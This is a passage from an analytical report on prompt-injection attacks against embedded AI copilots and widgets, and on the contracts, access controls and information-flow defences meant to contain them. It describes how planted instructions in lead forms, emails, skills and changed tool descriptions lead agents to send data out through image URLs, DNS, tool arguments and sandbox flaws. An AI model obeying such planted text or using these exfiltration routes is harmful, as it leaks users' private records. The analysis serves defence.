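| Parts portal | photos.example, every subdomain of cloud.example | Sent |

The union contains photos.example, charts.example and every subdomain of cloud.example. Two of the three hosts block the request, but the attacker can target the portal, which allows it. Removing cloud.example from the portal's list would stop this theft, but making the mail page even stricter would not.

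An attacker who can't choose the host can wait. Suppose Marta makes 10% of her requests in the portal, and ten of her requests bring the poisoned text into the context window. If each of the ten independently has that 10% chance of being made in the portal, the probability that at least one is made there is 1 − 0.9¹⁰, or about 65%.

The union covers only the addresses, though, and a theft also requires the right tools in the same host. If the portal's copilot can't search mail, it can't find the login code. The mail page's copilot can find the code but can't send it to the attacker. An easy precaution is therefore to give the copilot the fewest tools in the host with the loosest network rules. The precaution fails if Marta pastes the code into the portal herself. Shared memory would also weaken it, because an instruction saved in the mail page could then take effect in the portal.

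### Duties that each side leaves to the other

Rehberger argues more broadly that any AI widget made for other people's pages needs an explicit security contract with its host, a division of security duties that both sides understand. Otherwise, a widget that depends on a strict CSP can lose its protection when a customer copies it to another site. Published widget specifications settle some of these duties, but many widget makers and hosts probably rely on assumptions about each other.

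Suppose the bicycle maker buys a chat widget and builds it into the parts portal. The seller tested the widget on a demonstration site that blocks outside pictures. The portal allows pictures from anywhere because suppliers host their own product photos. Both decisions are reasonable, but nobody has written down who is responsible for stopping a reply from loading an attacker's picture.

| Duty | The widget's seller assumes | The bicycle maker assumes | What happens |
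|---|---|---|---|
| Sanitising output | The portal filters everything it displays | The widget produces safe replies | A planted picture or link reaches Marta's browser intact |
| Setting network rules | The portal has a strict CSP | The widget contacts only the seller's servers | The browser requests the picture and sends the data with it |
| Confirming actions | The portal asks before an email or order goes out | The widget asks before it acts | The copilot sends an email that nobody approved |
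| Logging | The portal records what the copilot does | The seller records it | After a theft, nobody can tell what the copilot read or sent |
| Clearing memory | The portal's staff delete planted memories after an attack | The seller deletes them | The instruction survives the clean-up and takes effect again |

Microsoft makes both the Microsoft 365 Copilot widget and its main hosts, so the missing contract would be between Microsoft's own teams, and a customer can't write it for them.

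A written duty also needs a rule for what happens if the responsible side fails to act. Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents, can send an agent's plan to an outside monitoring system for approval. If that system doesn't reply within one second, the agent goes ahead. This keeps agents working when the monitor breaks down. But customers can't rely on the monitor to approve every plan, and the plans that go unchecked may be the ones that take longest to assess.

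### ForcedLeak: a trusted domain that anyone could buy

Salesforce makes software for managing customer records, and its Agentforce agents can read and act on those records. In July 2025, Noma Security found that an outsider could steal the records with a form on a company's website. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature puts entries from such a form directly into the company's database as sales leads.

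This was ForcedLeak, the attack that sent data out through an expired domain. It had five steps:

1. The attacker submitted a form with hidden instructions in the description field, which had room for a long text.
2. An employee asked the agent an ordinary question about the new lead.
3. The agent answered the question and also followed the hidden instructions.
4. It looked up the email addresses of other leads and put them into the address of a picture.
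5. The employee's browser requested the picture and sent the email addresses to Noma's server.

Salesforce's CSP should have blocked the last step, but it still allowed the expired domain my-salesforce-cms.com. The Hacker News (2025) reports that anyone could have bought the domain for as little as $5. The planted text that Willison reproduces in *ForcedLeak* used a subdomain in the picture's URL, so the policy evidently allowed subdomains too.

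Noma and Salesforce, both quoted in *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025), emphasize different aspects of the flaw. Noma says the theft would have been impossible without a way around the CSP. That is right for this attack, though an attacker might have found a relay on another permitted domain. Salesforce doesn't mention the lapsed domain in its statement. It says it has released patches to stop agents from sending output to untrusted addresses, and that the security landscape for prompt injection is still evolving.

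The statement leaves out that the trusted list itself had to be corrected. Noma's address was on that list, so a stricter check against it would still have let the picture through. Noma reports that Salesforce regained control of the domain. Salesforce started enforcing its new list, Trusted URLs, on 8 September 2025, 42 days after Noma's report.

### What customers can reasonably be responsible for

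TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that, under the new rule, administrators had to list every outside domain their agents needed or risk disruption. A good argument for this is that a company knows better than Salesforce which outside services it uses. However, the company is less likely to know everything a server on each domain can do with a request.

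Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives docs.google.com as an example of an address to trust. In January 2026, Willison described a flaw in the email app Superhuman, whose content security policy (CSP) allowed images from that domain. Google Forms runs there and can save data sent in a URL, so an attacker could collect a victim's emails in a form. Superhuman had issued a fix by the time Willison wrote.

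Agentforce Coworker would not necessarily leak in the same way, because Salesforce lets administrators trust an address for some types of resource and not others. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* advises them to block images from a trusted domain unless the agent needs to display them. An administrator who follows the five steps in Salesforce's example would not learn this, because the steps cover only the name and address.

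Salesforce replaces any untrusted address in an agent's reply with a placeholder before the browser can request it. PromptArmor, a security company, considers the enforcement itself a powerful defence. But it analysed only the chat in Salesforce's own web app, so its analysis doesn't show whether the same agent is protected in another host.

SalesBleed, which Zenity Labs disclosed on 24 September 2026, could not have been prevented by even a carefully chosen list. According to *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026), this attack also began with a Web-to-Lead form, but it sent company names and deal sizes past the Trusted URLs check through the domain name system (DNS). A computer uses DNS to look up a server's name before contacting it. That query can reach a name server run by the domain's owner, so an attacker who puts stolen data into the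 name can receive it even if no picture loads. Salesforce fixed the flaw on 18 August 2026. Customers could not have fixed the check themselves, which is a strong reason to hold the vendor responsible for it.

It is less clear who should be responsible for confirming actions. In April 2026, Capsule Security described PipeLeak, an attack in which malicious instructions in a lead form made an Agentforce agent email customer records to an outsider. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) reports that Salesforce called the exfiltration path "configuration-specific" because customers could choose to require human approval. Capsule objected that manual approvals defeat the purpose of an autonomous agent and criticised the insecure defaults.

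Salesforce then said it had fixed the specific scenario and made human confirmation the default for emails sent by agents, according to Claw Times. Capsule was right about the defaults, since customers who never open the settings should not be the least protected. Its objection to approvals is weaker, because checking an outgoing email takes an employee a few seconds, and the agent can still read the leads, sort them and draft the replies by itself.

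## What the rules for embedded AI widgets specify and leave open

Salesforce could change that default on its own because it makes both the agent and the software around it. When one company's widget runs inside another company's assistant, the two companies have to agree on who does what, and published rules now settle part of this.

The rules build on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI assistants to outside tools and data. A company offers its tools through a program called an MCP server, and an assistant that connects to the server can call them. With an extension called MCP Apps, a tool can also return a widget, such as a map or a form, that appears in the conversation. Copilot is now the host and the widget comes from an outside company, whereas in the earlier examples Copilot was the widget and Outlook or SharePoint was the host.

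*SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025) sets out the specification for MCP Apps, whose stable version dates from 26 January 2026. The project's blog announced a new version of the core protocol on 28 July (Model Context Protocol, 2026). OpenAI's Apps SDK, a toolkit for building ChatGPT widgets, follows the MCP Apps standard with some additions. OpenAI now documents it under "plugins", and its *Plugin UI changelog* lists changes up to August 2026. Microsoft (2026) announced widgets for Microsoft 365 Copilot on 7 April, and its June documentation lists the parts of MCP Apps and the Apps SDK that Copilot supports.

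In the specification, "must" marks a requirement, "should" allows a host to depart from the rule for a good reason, and "may" leaves the choice to the host.

### One widget, from its domains to its first tool call

Suppose the bicycle maker's freight company offers a tracking widget. Marta asks Copilot where her late shipment is, Copilot calls the freight company's tool, and a map appears in the chat.

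The freight company decides which addresses to request for the widget. It declares one list for connections that the widget's scripts open, and another for pictures, scripts, stylesheets, fonts and media. Two more lists cover frames inside the widget and the base address for its relative links. If the company declares nothing, the widget can't load anything from outside.

Fonts and pictures share one list, so a developer can't repeat the mismatch in Copilot's HTML preview, where the font rule was looser than the picture rule. But a server trusted for fonts can receive picture requests too. A developer can also declare every subdomain of a domain at once, which carries the same risk as in the parts portal.

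Next, the host must put the widget in a sandboxed frame, meaning one with restricted abilities, and must build a CSP from the declared lists. For a widget that declares none, the required default includes these directives:

`default-src 'none'; img-src 'self' data:; connect-src 'none'`

This default also covers fonts, so the browser would block the kind of request Rehberger used. The host may shorten the freight company's lists but must not add to them. It should warn Marta if the widget needs outside domains, and it should log the policy.

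A host that is a web page must use two nested frames and load the outer one from a different origin (the combination of protocol, domain and port that browsers use to keep sites apart). The widget's scripts therefore can't read the chat page, its cookies or its stored data. Microsoft gives each MCP server's widgets their own web address, derived from the server's domain, which also separates the freight widget from, say, a payroll widget.

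The frame and the host then communicate through messages. The host must send the widget the complete arguments of the tool call that opened it, and the result once the tool finishes. The widget can send text back by posting a message in the chat with the role "user", which the host should preserve, or by supplying context for the model to use in later turns. The host may ask for Marta's consent to the chat message and may show her the text of the added context. The launch announcement lists the ability to "quietly update the model's context for later" among the advantages of widgets (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

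This ability is useful because if Marta clicks on one of five shipments on the map and types "when will it arrive?", she expects Copilot to know which one she means. But a malicious widget could use it for delayed tool invocation, without any email or document. Rule 2 would catch this only if the host counted text from widgets as untrusted. A message with the role "user" is worse, because to the model and most safeguards it looks like Marta's own request. The host could avoid this by labelling the text as the widget's, but the specification recommends the opposite.

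Finally, the widget can ask the host to call a tool on the widget's server. By default, both the model and the widget can call every tool. If the developer reserves a tool for the model, the host must refuse the widget's request. The host "may" require the user's approval before it passes on a call, but this is again optional. If the freight company has a tool for changing a delivery address, its widget could call that tool without Marta clicking anything.

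The specification may leave consent optional because consent dialogs are part of a host's design. The charter of the Model Context Protocol working group that maintains the extension puts host design outside the group's scope. Hosts also need some freedom, since a map that asked for permission at every zoom would be impractical. But the specification could require confirmation for calls that change or send something and still let each host decide how the dialog looks.

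### Where the three sets of rules differ

| | MCP Apps | OpenAI | Microsoft |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolation | Sandboxed frame required, with a second frame in web hosts | Isolated frame; frames inside it off by default | Separate web address for each server's widgets; frames inside them unsupported |
| Network default | No outside addresses | Strict CSP; developers must list the exact domains for review | Supports the declared lists for connections and resources; states no default |
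| Tool permissions | Model and widget can both call a tool unless the developer restricts it | Supports widget tool calls; requires correct safety labels on tools | Supports hiding a tool from the model, but not OpenAI's setting for widget access |
| User consent | Host may ask | Tells developers to require confirmation for irreversible actions | Asks before an agent connects to a server; ignores the "destructive" label on tools |
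| Logging | Host should log each CSP; also advises logging widgets' requests | Tells developers to keep audit logs and remove personal data | Doesn't support log messages sent by widgets |
| Changes after approval | No rule on renewed consent | Automated checks before eligible updates go live | Agent's developer stores tool descriptions in a file |

Microsoft's entry on logging covers only the messages a widget writes about itself, so Microsoft may still keep a record of what Copilot did.

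Most of OpenAI's consent and logging rules apply to the widget's developer. OpenAI's *Security & Privacy* advises developers to check every input on their own server and to assume that injected prompts will reach it. A dishonest developer can ignore this advice, so the host needs controls that work without the developer's cooperation.

Hosts don't follow every requirement either. The specification requires a host to notify a widget when a tool call is cancelled and before removing the widget. Microsoft lists both notices as unsupported. Neither is important for preventing data theft, but a developer can't assume that a host follows a security rule just because the specification requires it.

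Tool permissions are a more serious example. MCP Apps has a single setting for who can call a tool, while OpenAI originally had two, one for the model and one for the widget. Microsoft's documentation matches both to the MCP Apps setting, but lists the model setting as supported and the widget setting as unsupported. A developer who reserves a tool for the model apparently can't rely on Copilot to block the widget from calling it.

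The three also differ on which data the model can see. Under the specification, the `structuredContent` part of a tool's result goes to the widget and stays out of the model's context. OpenAI tells developers that the model reads this part verbatim, and Microsoft describes it as data for both the widget and the model. If the freight company puts the warehouse gate code there for the widget to display, a host that follows the specification would keep it from a hijacked model, but ChatGPT and Copilot would give it to the model. The developer can avoid this by putting the code in `_meta`, a field that all three reserve for the widget.

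Some mismatches are safe. In *MCP Apps open standard migration*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a developer reported that a published widget's resources didn't appear in ChatGPT until the developer repeated the domain list in OpenAI's older format. The mismatch broke the widget but didn't give it access to any address the developer had left out.

### A correctly isolated widget that receives stolen data

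The specification's list of possible attacks includes a malicious server, a widget that tries to escape its frame and a widget that steals data from the host. In all of these, the attacker controls the server or the widget, and the list doesn't include a hijacked model.

Suppose the freight company is honest and its widget declares no outside domains. Its tracking tool takes a shipment number and an optional note to the sender, such as a request to call before delivery. The sender is the supplier whose email contains hidden instructions. When Marta asks about the shipment, Copilot reads the email, finds rival suppliers' prices in her correspondence and puts them in the note.

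Copilot sends the note to the freight company's server as part of the tool call. It must also pass the complete arguments to the widget, which displays the note beside the map. The supplier then opens the freight company's tracking page and reads the prices. Throughout, the widget stays in its frame and the browser contacts only declared addresses.

Frame isolation would have stopped other attacks. This table adds a dishonest widget to the same example:

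| Attempt | What the specification provides |
|---|---|
| The widget tries to read a login code on the chat page | The browser refuses, because the widget has a different origin |
| The widget requests a picture from an undeclared server | The CSP blocks the request |
| The hijacked model puts the prices in the note | The host sends them to the server and the widget |
| The widget sends the prices to its own server in another tool call | The host may ask Marta first |
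| The widget asks the host to open a link containing the prices | The host should open it; there is no duty to ask or to check the declared domains |

Isolation controls what the widget can take for itself. It doesn't control what the host gives it, or where the widget's server sends the data afterwards. Let A be the set of declared domains, s the widget's own server, and F(s) every address that this server contacts. Even without links or relays on the declared domains, data given to the widget can reach:

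`A ∪ {s} ∪ F(s)`

A careful developer can leave the widget's list of allowed domains empty, but data can still reach the developer's server because tool calls go through the host and aren't subject to the browser's network rules. The host can't limit where that server then sends the data. OpenAI notes that code on the server has no network restrictions except those of its hosting environment.

Frames inside a widget can extend the set of reachable domains further. When OpenAI permits a frame, the page inside follows its own CSP, not the widget's domain lists. OpenAI therefore tells developers to keep the permitted addresses specific and to include the embedded page in their security review. Microsoft avoids this problem by not supporting such frames.

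A change in ChatGPT does address the data itself. If a tool needs the user's approval, the widget may have to wait for its input until the user approves the call. In the freight example, Marta could then stop the theft before the server or the widget received the note, but only if the approval dialog showed her the note.

### When a tool changes after approval

In the freight example, the hidden instructions arrived by email. They can also come from a tool's description, which the model reads to decide when and how to call the tool.

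On 30 June 2026, Microsoft described how an attacker could exploit this. In its example, a finance team builds an agent in Copilot Studio to help analysts with invoices. The agent can use the company's list of approved vendors, Outlook, and an outside MCP server that checks vendors' bank details. The head of the team responsible approves the outside server without a separate security review.

A developer then updates the server. The tool's name and the summary shown to users stay the same, but its description now includes hidden instructions to collect the last thirty unpaid invoices and send a summary of them with each check, supposedly to detect fraud. Some configurations accept a new description without asking for approval again. The next time an analyst asks a routine question about a supplier, the agent sends the invoice summary along with the bank details. The server returns a plausible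 answer and passes the summary to the attacker.

This is a scenario, not a documented incident. Microsoft calls it an "attack pattern" and names no victim, date or amount of stolen data. It says such techniques were "observed in 2026 against a growing range of enterprise agents", but that it isn't disclosing details of any specific affected organisation. A real case may lie behind the scenario, but outsiders can't tell from the account. The scenario also doesn't involve a widget. According to Voitanos' *What are MCP Apps* (2026), Copilot in June displayed widgets only in agents built with a different tool, the Agents Toolkit for Visual Studio Code.

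The scenario still applies to widgets, because they come from the same servers and depend on the same tool descriptions. Every step in it was permitted, since the server was on the approved list, the analyst had access to the invoices, and the agent was allowed to call the tool. The approval covered only the server's name, so it did not catch a later change to the tool description, which contained the attack. Microsoft recommends treating such a change like a change to the agent's standing instructions.

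A host can detect the change by storing a fingerprint of what someone approved:

`fingerprint = hash(tool descriptions, input fields, widget code, declared domains)`

A hash is a short code computed from a text, and in practice any edit to the text produces a different code. If the new hash doesn't match the approved one, the host keeps using the old version or suspends the tool until someone approves the new version. The reviewer can see just the lines that changed. In Microsoft's scenario, those lines would have contained a request for thirty invoices in a tool meant to check bank details.

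The MCP Apps specification suggests fingerprints for the widget's code, without a "must" or "should", but doesn't mention them for tool descriptions. The July version of the core protocol doesn't fill this gap. It lets a server state how long a host can keep its copy of the tool list, which affects when a new description arrives but doesn't ensure that anyone has read it. Its new twelve-month notice period covers features removed from the protocol, not changes to a company's tools.

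OpenAI has had a stricter rule. *Widget uri versioning and app resubmission*, another thread on its forum, quotes instructions under which tool names, signatures and descriptions were locked after publication and developers had to resubmit the app to change them. In *How to surface mcp server updates for an existing plugin*, a reply signed "Mark G." explains that ChatGPT used a reviewed snapshot of the descriptions and that reconnecting to the server would not refresh it.

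The process now seems faster. OpenAI tells developers that it automatically picks up changes to a published plugin's server, and that eligible updates go live once they pass automated checks. Honest developers wait less, and users get security fixes sooner. But an automated check that looks for malicious wording is a guardrail, and it may miss instructions like those in Microsoft's scenario, which were disguised as formatting guidance.

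The developer of a declarative agent, the kind that can display widgets in Microsoft 365 Copilot, describes each tool in a manifest, a configuration file stored with the agent. Connell calls these descriptions static in *Integrate an MCP Apps server into a Microsoft 365 Copilot declarative agent*, so a new description on the server should not reach the model until the developer updates the manifest. That would have prevented the change in the finance scenario from taking effect unnoticed, though the server could still put instructions in a tool's result.

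In *Clarification on MCP Server URL and Versioning During ChatGPT App Update Submission*, a developer reported that ChatGPT dropped the old widget code before OpenAI had approved the new version, and then tried to load code that no longer existed. The tool descriptions, meanwhile, stayed fixed. If widget code and tool descriptions can change separately, users may get a combination that the reviewer didn't approve. Each approval therefore needs a version number that covers the descriptions, input fields, widget code and domains together.

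Caching can also keep a bad widget version in use. MCP Community's *MCP Apps in Practice* (2026) warns developers that edited widget code may not appear, because hosts can store copies and the server's expiry time is only a hint. After a theft, a customer needs a way to withdraw a version immediately, without waiting for cached copies to expire.

The best argument against renewed consent is that servers change often, and people who have to approve every corrected typo will stop reading the requests. The host could let changes to colours or layout through after an automated check, and ask again only if the update changes a description, adds an input field, contacts a new domain or gives the widget another tool. It should ask an administrator rather than Marta, who has no reason to know what a tool description is.

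Even then, the fingerprint covers only what is visible to the host. The operator of the server that checks bank details could start selling those details without changing the description. Renewed consent can't prevent that, so the host also has to limit the data it sends.

### The least a contract should contain

The MCP Apps specification already requires a sandboxed frame and a CSP limited to declared domains. A contract that also covered a hijacked model and a changed tool would need at least these clauses:

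1. The host gives each server's widgets a separate origin and blocks all outside addresses by default. Links that a widget asks to open follow the same rules as pictures and connections.
2. The widget's maker states which data each tool needs and why. The host checks the arguments before they leave and removes or refuses anything else.
3. Text from a widget or a tool stays labelled as outside text, including in later turns. The host never presents it to the model as the user's words.
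4. A widget can call only the tools that the approved version lists for it. Before a call sends data to a new recipient or makes a lasting change, the host shows the user the exact content in its own dialog.
5. Approval applies to one version. A changed description, input field, domain or permission needs new approval, and the customer can withdraw a version at once.
6. The host records each call, the version in use, the kind of data sent and who approved it. The widget's maker keeps matching records of what its server did with the data.
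7. If a check fails or doesn't answer in time, the host refuses the action. After an attack, each side deletes the stored instructions and data under its control by an agreed deadline.

The second clause would be the hardest to enforce. Software can check a shipment number because it has a fixed format, but a free-text note can contain anything, including a price list. The freight company could replace the note with a few set phrases, and Marta could call the supplier about anything else.

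Tests could enforce some of the other clauses. The working group's charter lists a suite of tests for sandboxing, permissions, CSP and auditability among its criteria for success. Such tests can check that a host blocks an undeclared domain or refuses a forbidden tool call. The specification has no rule for tool descriptions that change after approval, but if it did, tests could cover that too. The test server would alter one sentence of an approved description, and the host would pass if it stopped calling the tool.

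## Containment: limiting data, actions and network access

A host can pass all of these tests while its model follows a supplier's hidden instructions. Containment uses software outside the model to limit what a hijacked assistant can reach, do or send. Designers who rely on it expect some injections to succeed, and results from defences inside the model support that expectation.

### What training and filters achieve

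Shi and colleagues at Google DeepMind used automated search to write hidden texts that made Gemini 2.0 send out private details such as a passport number. Against the undefended model, a highly successful text cost less than $10 to produce. They then tested eight defences against each of three search methods. The defences included a warning in the prompt, a filter for unnatural text and a second model that judged whether an attack had taken place. In 16 of the 24 combinations, an adaptive attack, meaning one developed against the defended model, did at least as well as an attack developed without the defence.

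For Gemini 2.5, Google trained the model itself on attacks paired with safe answers. A set of attack texts that had worked on Gemini 2.0 92% of the time now worked only 18% of the time. Adaptive attacks gave a less reassuring picture:

| Search method | Task | Best success rate, Gemini 2.0 | Best success rate, Gemini 2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| TAP | Email | 99.8% | 53.6% |
| TAP | Calendar | 100% | 94.6% |
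| Actor-critic | Email | 66.2% | 40.8% |
| Actor-critic | Calendar | 96.8% | 59.6% |
| Beam search | Email | 74.8% | 4.2% |
| Beam search | Calendar | 98.6% | 0% |

TAP and actor-critic produce ordinary sentences, while beam search adds strings of random-looking tokens. The new model resisted the strings almost completely but did much worse against TAP, especially in the calendar task. Google trained the model with the email tool but not the calendar tool, which may explain part of the difference. The rates are for the model alone, without the other protections in Google's products.

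*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that adaptive attackers broke twelve published defences, most of them with success rates above 90%. It also cites Anthropic's results for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance, a hundred attempts would succeed 99% of the time (1 − 0.953¹⁰⁰), so the model evidently held out in some cases however often the attackers tried.

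A filter's measured effectiveness also depends on the test. In *CAITLYN* (2026), a language model used as a judge cut the attack success rate from 16.8% to zero on AgentDojo, a widely used set of simulated office, travel and banking tasks. On another benchmark, SafeClawBench, the same kind of judge cut the rate only from 33.3% to 24.2%. The attacks were fixed and did not adapt to the judge.

Shi and colleagues reply that an incomplete defence can still be worthwhile because it makes attacks harder and more expensive. Their figures only partly support this. Beam search became nearly useless, but TAP needed half as many queries to find its best calendar attack on Gemini 2.5 (2,160) as it did on Gemini 2.0.

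The argument applies better to attackers who reuse old texts. At a success rate of 92%, they need about 1.1 emails per theft on average, and at 18% they need about 5.6. The extra emails would make little difference to a spammer, but someone who has one chance to reach a finance director, or who fears that a failed attempt will alert the company, might give up. An organisation should therefore keep its filters, but it can't use them to work out the most it could lose.

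### What the assistant can read

Because Copilot has its user's access, the simplest limit is to give users less access. If Marta can still open the payroll folder from an old project, a hijacked Copilot can open it too. That access can be removed without affecting her work. But narrower permissions don't protect the information she needs as a buyer, including the prices from rival companies that the supplier wants to see.

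*Position* (Bhatt, Rajore and colleagues, 2025), a paper by Microsoft researchers, proposes checking the permissions of everyone in an exchange instead of only the user's. In its example, Bob emails Alice to suggest a meeting. The email contains hidden instructions for her assistant to look up a project's revenue and propose the date that matches the figure in millions. Alice asks for a draft reply. The revenue is $7 million, so the draft suggests 7 May, and she approves it because nothing looks wrong. A filter that scans outgoing text for confidential figures would probably miss it too.

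Participant-aware access control keeps the revenue figure away from the model in the first place. If P is the set of people in the exchange, the software retrieves a document d only if all of them may read it:

`P ⊆ readers(d)`

When an assistant drafts Alice's reply to Bob, the software leaves out the revenue report because Bob can't open it. If Bob copies in Charlie, the assistant can use the report only if Alice, Bob and Charlie all have access to it. If Alice reviews each draft, the software can ask her to allow an exception. If the assistant sends messages without her review, it has to write them without the report.

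This protection works however the attacker words the instructions, but it is strict. Copilot could not help Marta answer the supplier on the basis of their contract. The supplier has his own signed copy, but the software can check only the file's permissions, and he has no permission to open the bicycle maker's file. Bhatt and colleagues also acknowledge that access lists can be wrong.

The protection also depends on who counts as a participant. If the software counts only Marta, because only she receives the summary she asked for, Copilot can still retrieve the rival prices and put them in an image's URL. If it also counts the supplier, because his email is part of the input, Copilot can't compare that email with the contract.

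Microsoft has adopted the principle in Copilot Tuning, a product that trains models on a company's documents. A person may use such a model only if they can open every document in its training data. Adding documents gives the model more information but usually reduces the number of people who may use it. This check doesn't stop a poisoned email. Doing so would require applying the same check when Copilot retrieves documents to answer a question. Bhatt and colleagues propose this but describe no product that does it.

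### What it can do without asking

Approval dialogs limit a copilot's actions, but Cowork's did not cover emails and Teams messages addressed to the user. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reported in May 2026 that Cowork sent these messages immediately and that users had no setting to change this.

The exception for messages to yourself can leak data even though you are the only recipient. Emails and Teams messages can contain pictures from outside servers, which the user's computer requests when the user opens the message. Cowork could also obtain links that let anyone download a file without logging in. By putting such a link into a picture's address, an attacker could get a whole file instead of a few words.

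PromptArmor planted its instructions in a skill, a file that tells Cowork how to do a type of task. Users often find skills online and upload them. Five of this skill's 81 lines were malicious. The test user, who had files containing financial and personal data, asked Cowork for a recap of the week's work. Cowork used the skill and posted a recap to the user in Teams. Opening it sent the files' download links to a server standing in for the attacker's. Cowork's activity display showed that it had posted a message, but not what the message contained.

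The attack worked in all five trials. That shows the result was not a fluke, but five trials are too few to estimate the success rate precisely, since an attack that works only 55% of the time would succeed five times in a row in about one series out of twenty. PromptArmor first tested Cowork's automatic setting, which switches between Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. The same planted text also worked with Opus 4.7 selected directly, and more documents leaked because that model searched more thoroughly for recent ones.

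PromptArmor treats the problem as a risk of the product's design, not a specific bug, and reports no fix. Its main advice is to reduce excessive permissions. Administrators can also block downloads from particular SharePoint sites or for files with a particular sensitivity label, which stops Cowork from obtaining download links. Users can then view those files only in a browser, and can't print or synchronise them or open them in desktop Word or Excel. That may be acceptable for payroll records but would be a nuisance for a spreadsheet that staff edit every day.

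A better approval rule would depend on what a message can do as well as who receives it. Cowork could remove externally hosted pictures from any message it writes, or ask the user for approval whenever a message contains an external web address. The preview in the approval dialog would have to show the address as text, because loading the picture would send the data out before the user had decided.

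### Where its code can connect

Copilot and Cowork can also run code, for example to compare two documents. They run it in a sandbox, an isolated environment that is supposed to have no access to outside servers. If the isolation works, malicious code could read data and perform calculations but could not send the results to an outside server.

This isolation failed twice in 2026. PromptArmor's *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control* describes a flaw that let code in Cowork's sandbox contact an attacker's server. The attacker could send commands and receive emails, SharePoint files and chat history in return. Pressing the stop button did not end the attack. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June, and Microsoft had mitigated it by 19 August.

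The other failure was the third ReLeak chain, in which code run by Microsoft 365 Copilot sent confidential data directly to an outside server. Faisal lists it as CVE-2026-78501, with a score of 8.6. Microsoft fixed it on 17 September 2026.

Even so, a sandbox protects better than a guardrail, because once engineers fix a flaw in it, rewording an injection won't bring the flaw back. But deterministic limits can still have bugs, so a company shouldn't depend on just one. Cowork's sandbox could reach the user's mail and files through connected services, and its flaw would have exposed less if that access had been narrower.

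Even a flawless sandbox can't filter permitted messages by their content. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that if the sandbox allows email, a hijacked assistant can put secrets in a plausible email. The connection to the mail server looks the same whether the message contains a delivery date or a list of rival prices. To block only the prices, software has to track where the contents of the message came from.

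### Labels that stay with the data

In information-flow control, software labels each piece of data, passes the label on to anything made from that data, and checks the labels before a tool call. Costa, Köpf and colleagues developed one such system, FIDES, at Microsoft and describe it in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025).

A label in FIDES records whether the source is trusted and who may read the data. When the software combines several items, the result is trusted only if every item is, and only people who may read every item may read the result:

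`trusted(result) = trusted(item 1) AND trusted(item 2) AND ...`

`readers(result) = readers(item 1) ∩ readers(item 2) ∩ ...`

For example, suppose Marta and her manager are allowed to read an internal memo, and Marta and a supplier are allowed to read the supplier's email. Only Marta is allowed to read a text that draws on both, and the text is untrusted because the email is untrusted.

The conversation as a whole also has a label, which covers everything the model has received so far. A new turn doesn't reset it. Before each tool call, the software applies a fixed policy, and two rules are the most important:

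- A consequential action, such as sending a message or changing a record, requires a trusted context.
- Data may go to a recipient only if that recipient is among its permitted readers.

The software can apply both rules without relying on a model's judgement. An injection may cause the model to request anything, but it can't change the labels.

### A delayed attack, step by step

Suppose the supplier's email tells Copilot to wait until Marta says thanks, then find the rival prices and email them to him. In a simple system that tracks labels but hides nothing from the model, the attack goes like this:

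| Turn | Requested step | Conversation before the step | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read the supplier's email | Trusted; anyone may read it | Allowed, because reading is not consequential |
| 2 | Search Marta's mail for rival prices | Untrusted; Marta and the supplier may read it | Allowed, for the same reason |
| 2 | Email the prices to the supplier | Untrusted; only Marta may read it | Refused under both rules |

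The thank-you doesn't help the attacker, because the label from turn 1 still applies. Rule 2 from the earlier two-rule model would have blocked both the search and the email. FIDES can allow the search but block the email, so Marta could still ask Copilot to find the contract at turn 2. The policy would also block a delayed request to save a memory, like the one in the biography attack that Embrace The Red documents, if the designers classified saving a memory as consequential.

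The table covers only tool calls. Costa and colleagues treat replies to the user as harmless by default but note that a system can check them too. Copilot would need this check because several attacks on it sent data out through an image or font in the reply. The policy would have to treat an outside address in a reply as a message to whoever runs the server at that address.

The simple system also prevents Marta from having Copilot send anything to anyone after it has read the supplier's email, even a summary for her manager. FIDES avoids this by hiding untrusted text from the model that plans the work. The planning model receives a placeholder, such as "email 1", instead of the email's body. It can have a separate model, which has no tools, summarise email 1, and the software stores the summary under another placeholder. The planning model then calls the mail tool to send that summary to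 the manager.

The supplier's text never reaches the model that chooses the actions, so the conversation stays trusted and the instruction to wait for a thank-you has no effect. The manager isn't on the email's reader list, but the policy can let Marta override the list, since she gave the order to send and no untrusted text influenced it.

Some tasks require passing information from the hidden text to the planning model. If Marta asks Copilot to add a meeting to her calendar whenever an email requests one, the planning model's next step depends on whether the email does. FIDES can restrict the separate model's answer to yes or no. A policy may allow that answer, because an attacker can't fit new instructions into one bit. But the attacker can still choose the answer and put an unwanted meeting in her calendar.

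### CaMeL and the fixed plan

Google DeepMind's CaMeL applies a similar separation to the whole plan. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) explains that one model writes the plan from the user's request alone, while another, which has no tools, reads untrusted data. The interpreter that carries out the plan records where each value came from and checks the policy before every tool call.

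For Marta's original request, the plan would be to fetch the email and the contract, have the reading model summarise the email and look for conflicts, and show her the answer. The email can affect the answer but can't add a step to the plan.

Like other plan-then-execute designs, CaMeL must maintain its separation for the whole conversation, or a delayed attack could get around it. When Marta says thanks, the planning model must receive her words without the supplier's text.

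Bhatt and colleagues object that the meeting-date attack would still work against CaMeL, because its policies can't detect a revenue figure disguised as a date. This seems too pessimistic if the labels follow the data's origin. If a model writes "7 May" based on the revenue report, that text carries the report's label, and Bob isn't one of the report's permitted readers. The objection is stronger if the system asks Alice to approve an exception, because she would see only a date.

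### Benchmark results and lost usefulness

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the model. They counted successful injections, and in separate runs without attacks they measured the share of ordinary tasks that the assistant completed. "Basic" is a planner that hides nothing from the model:

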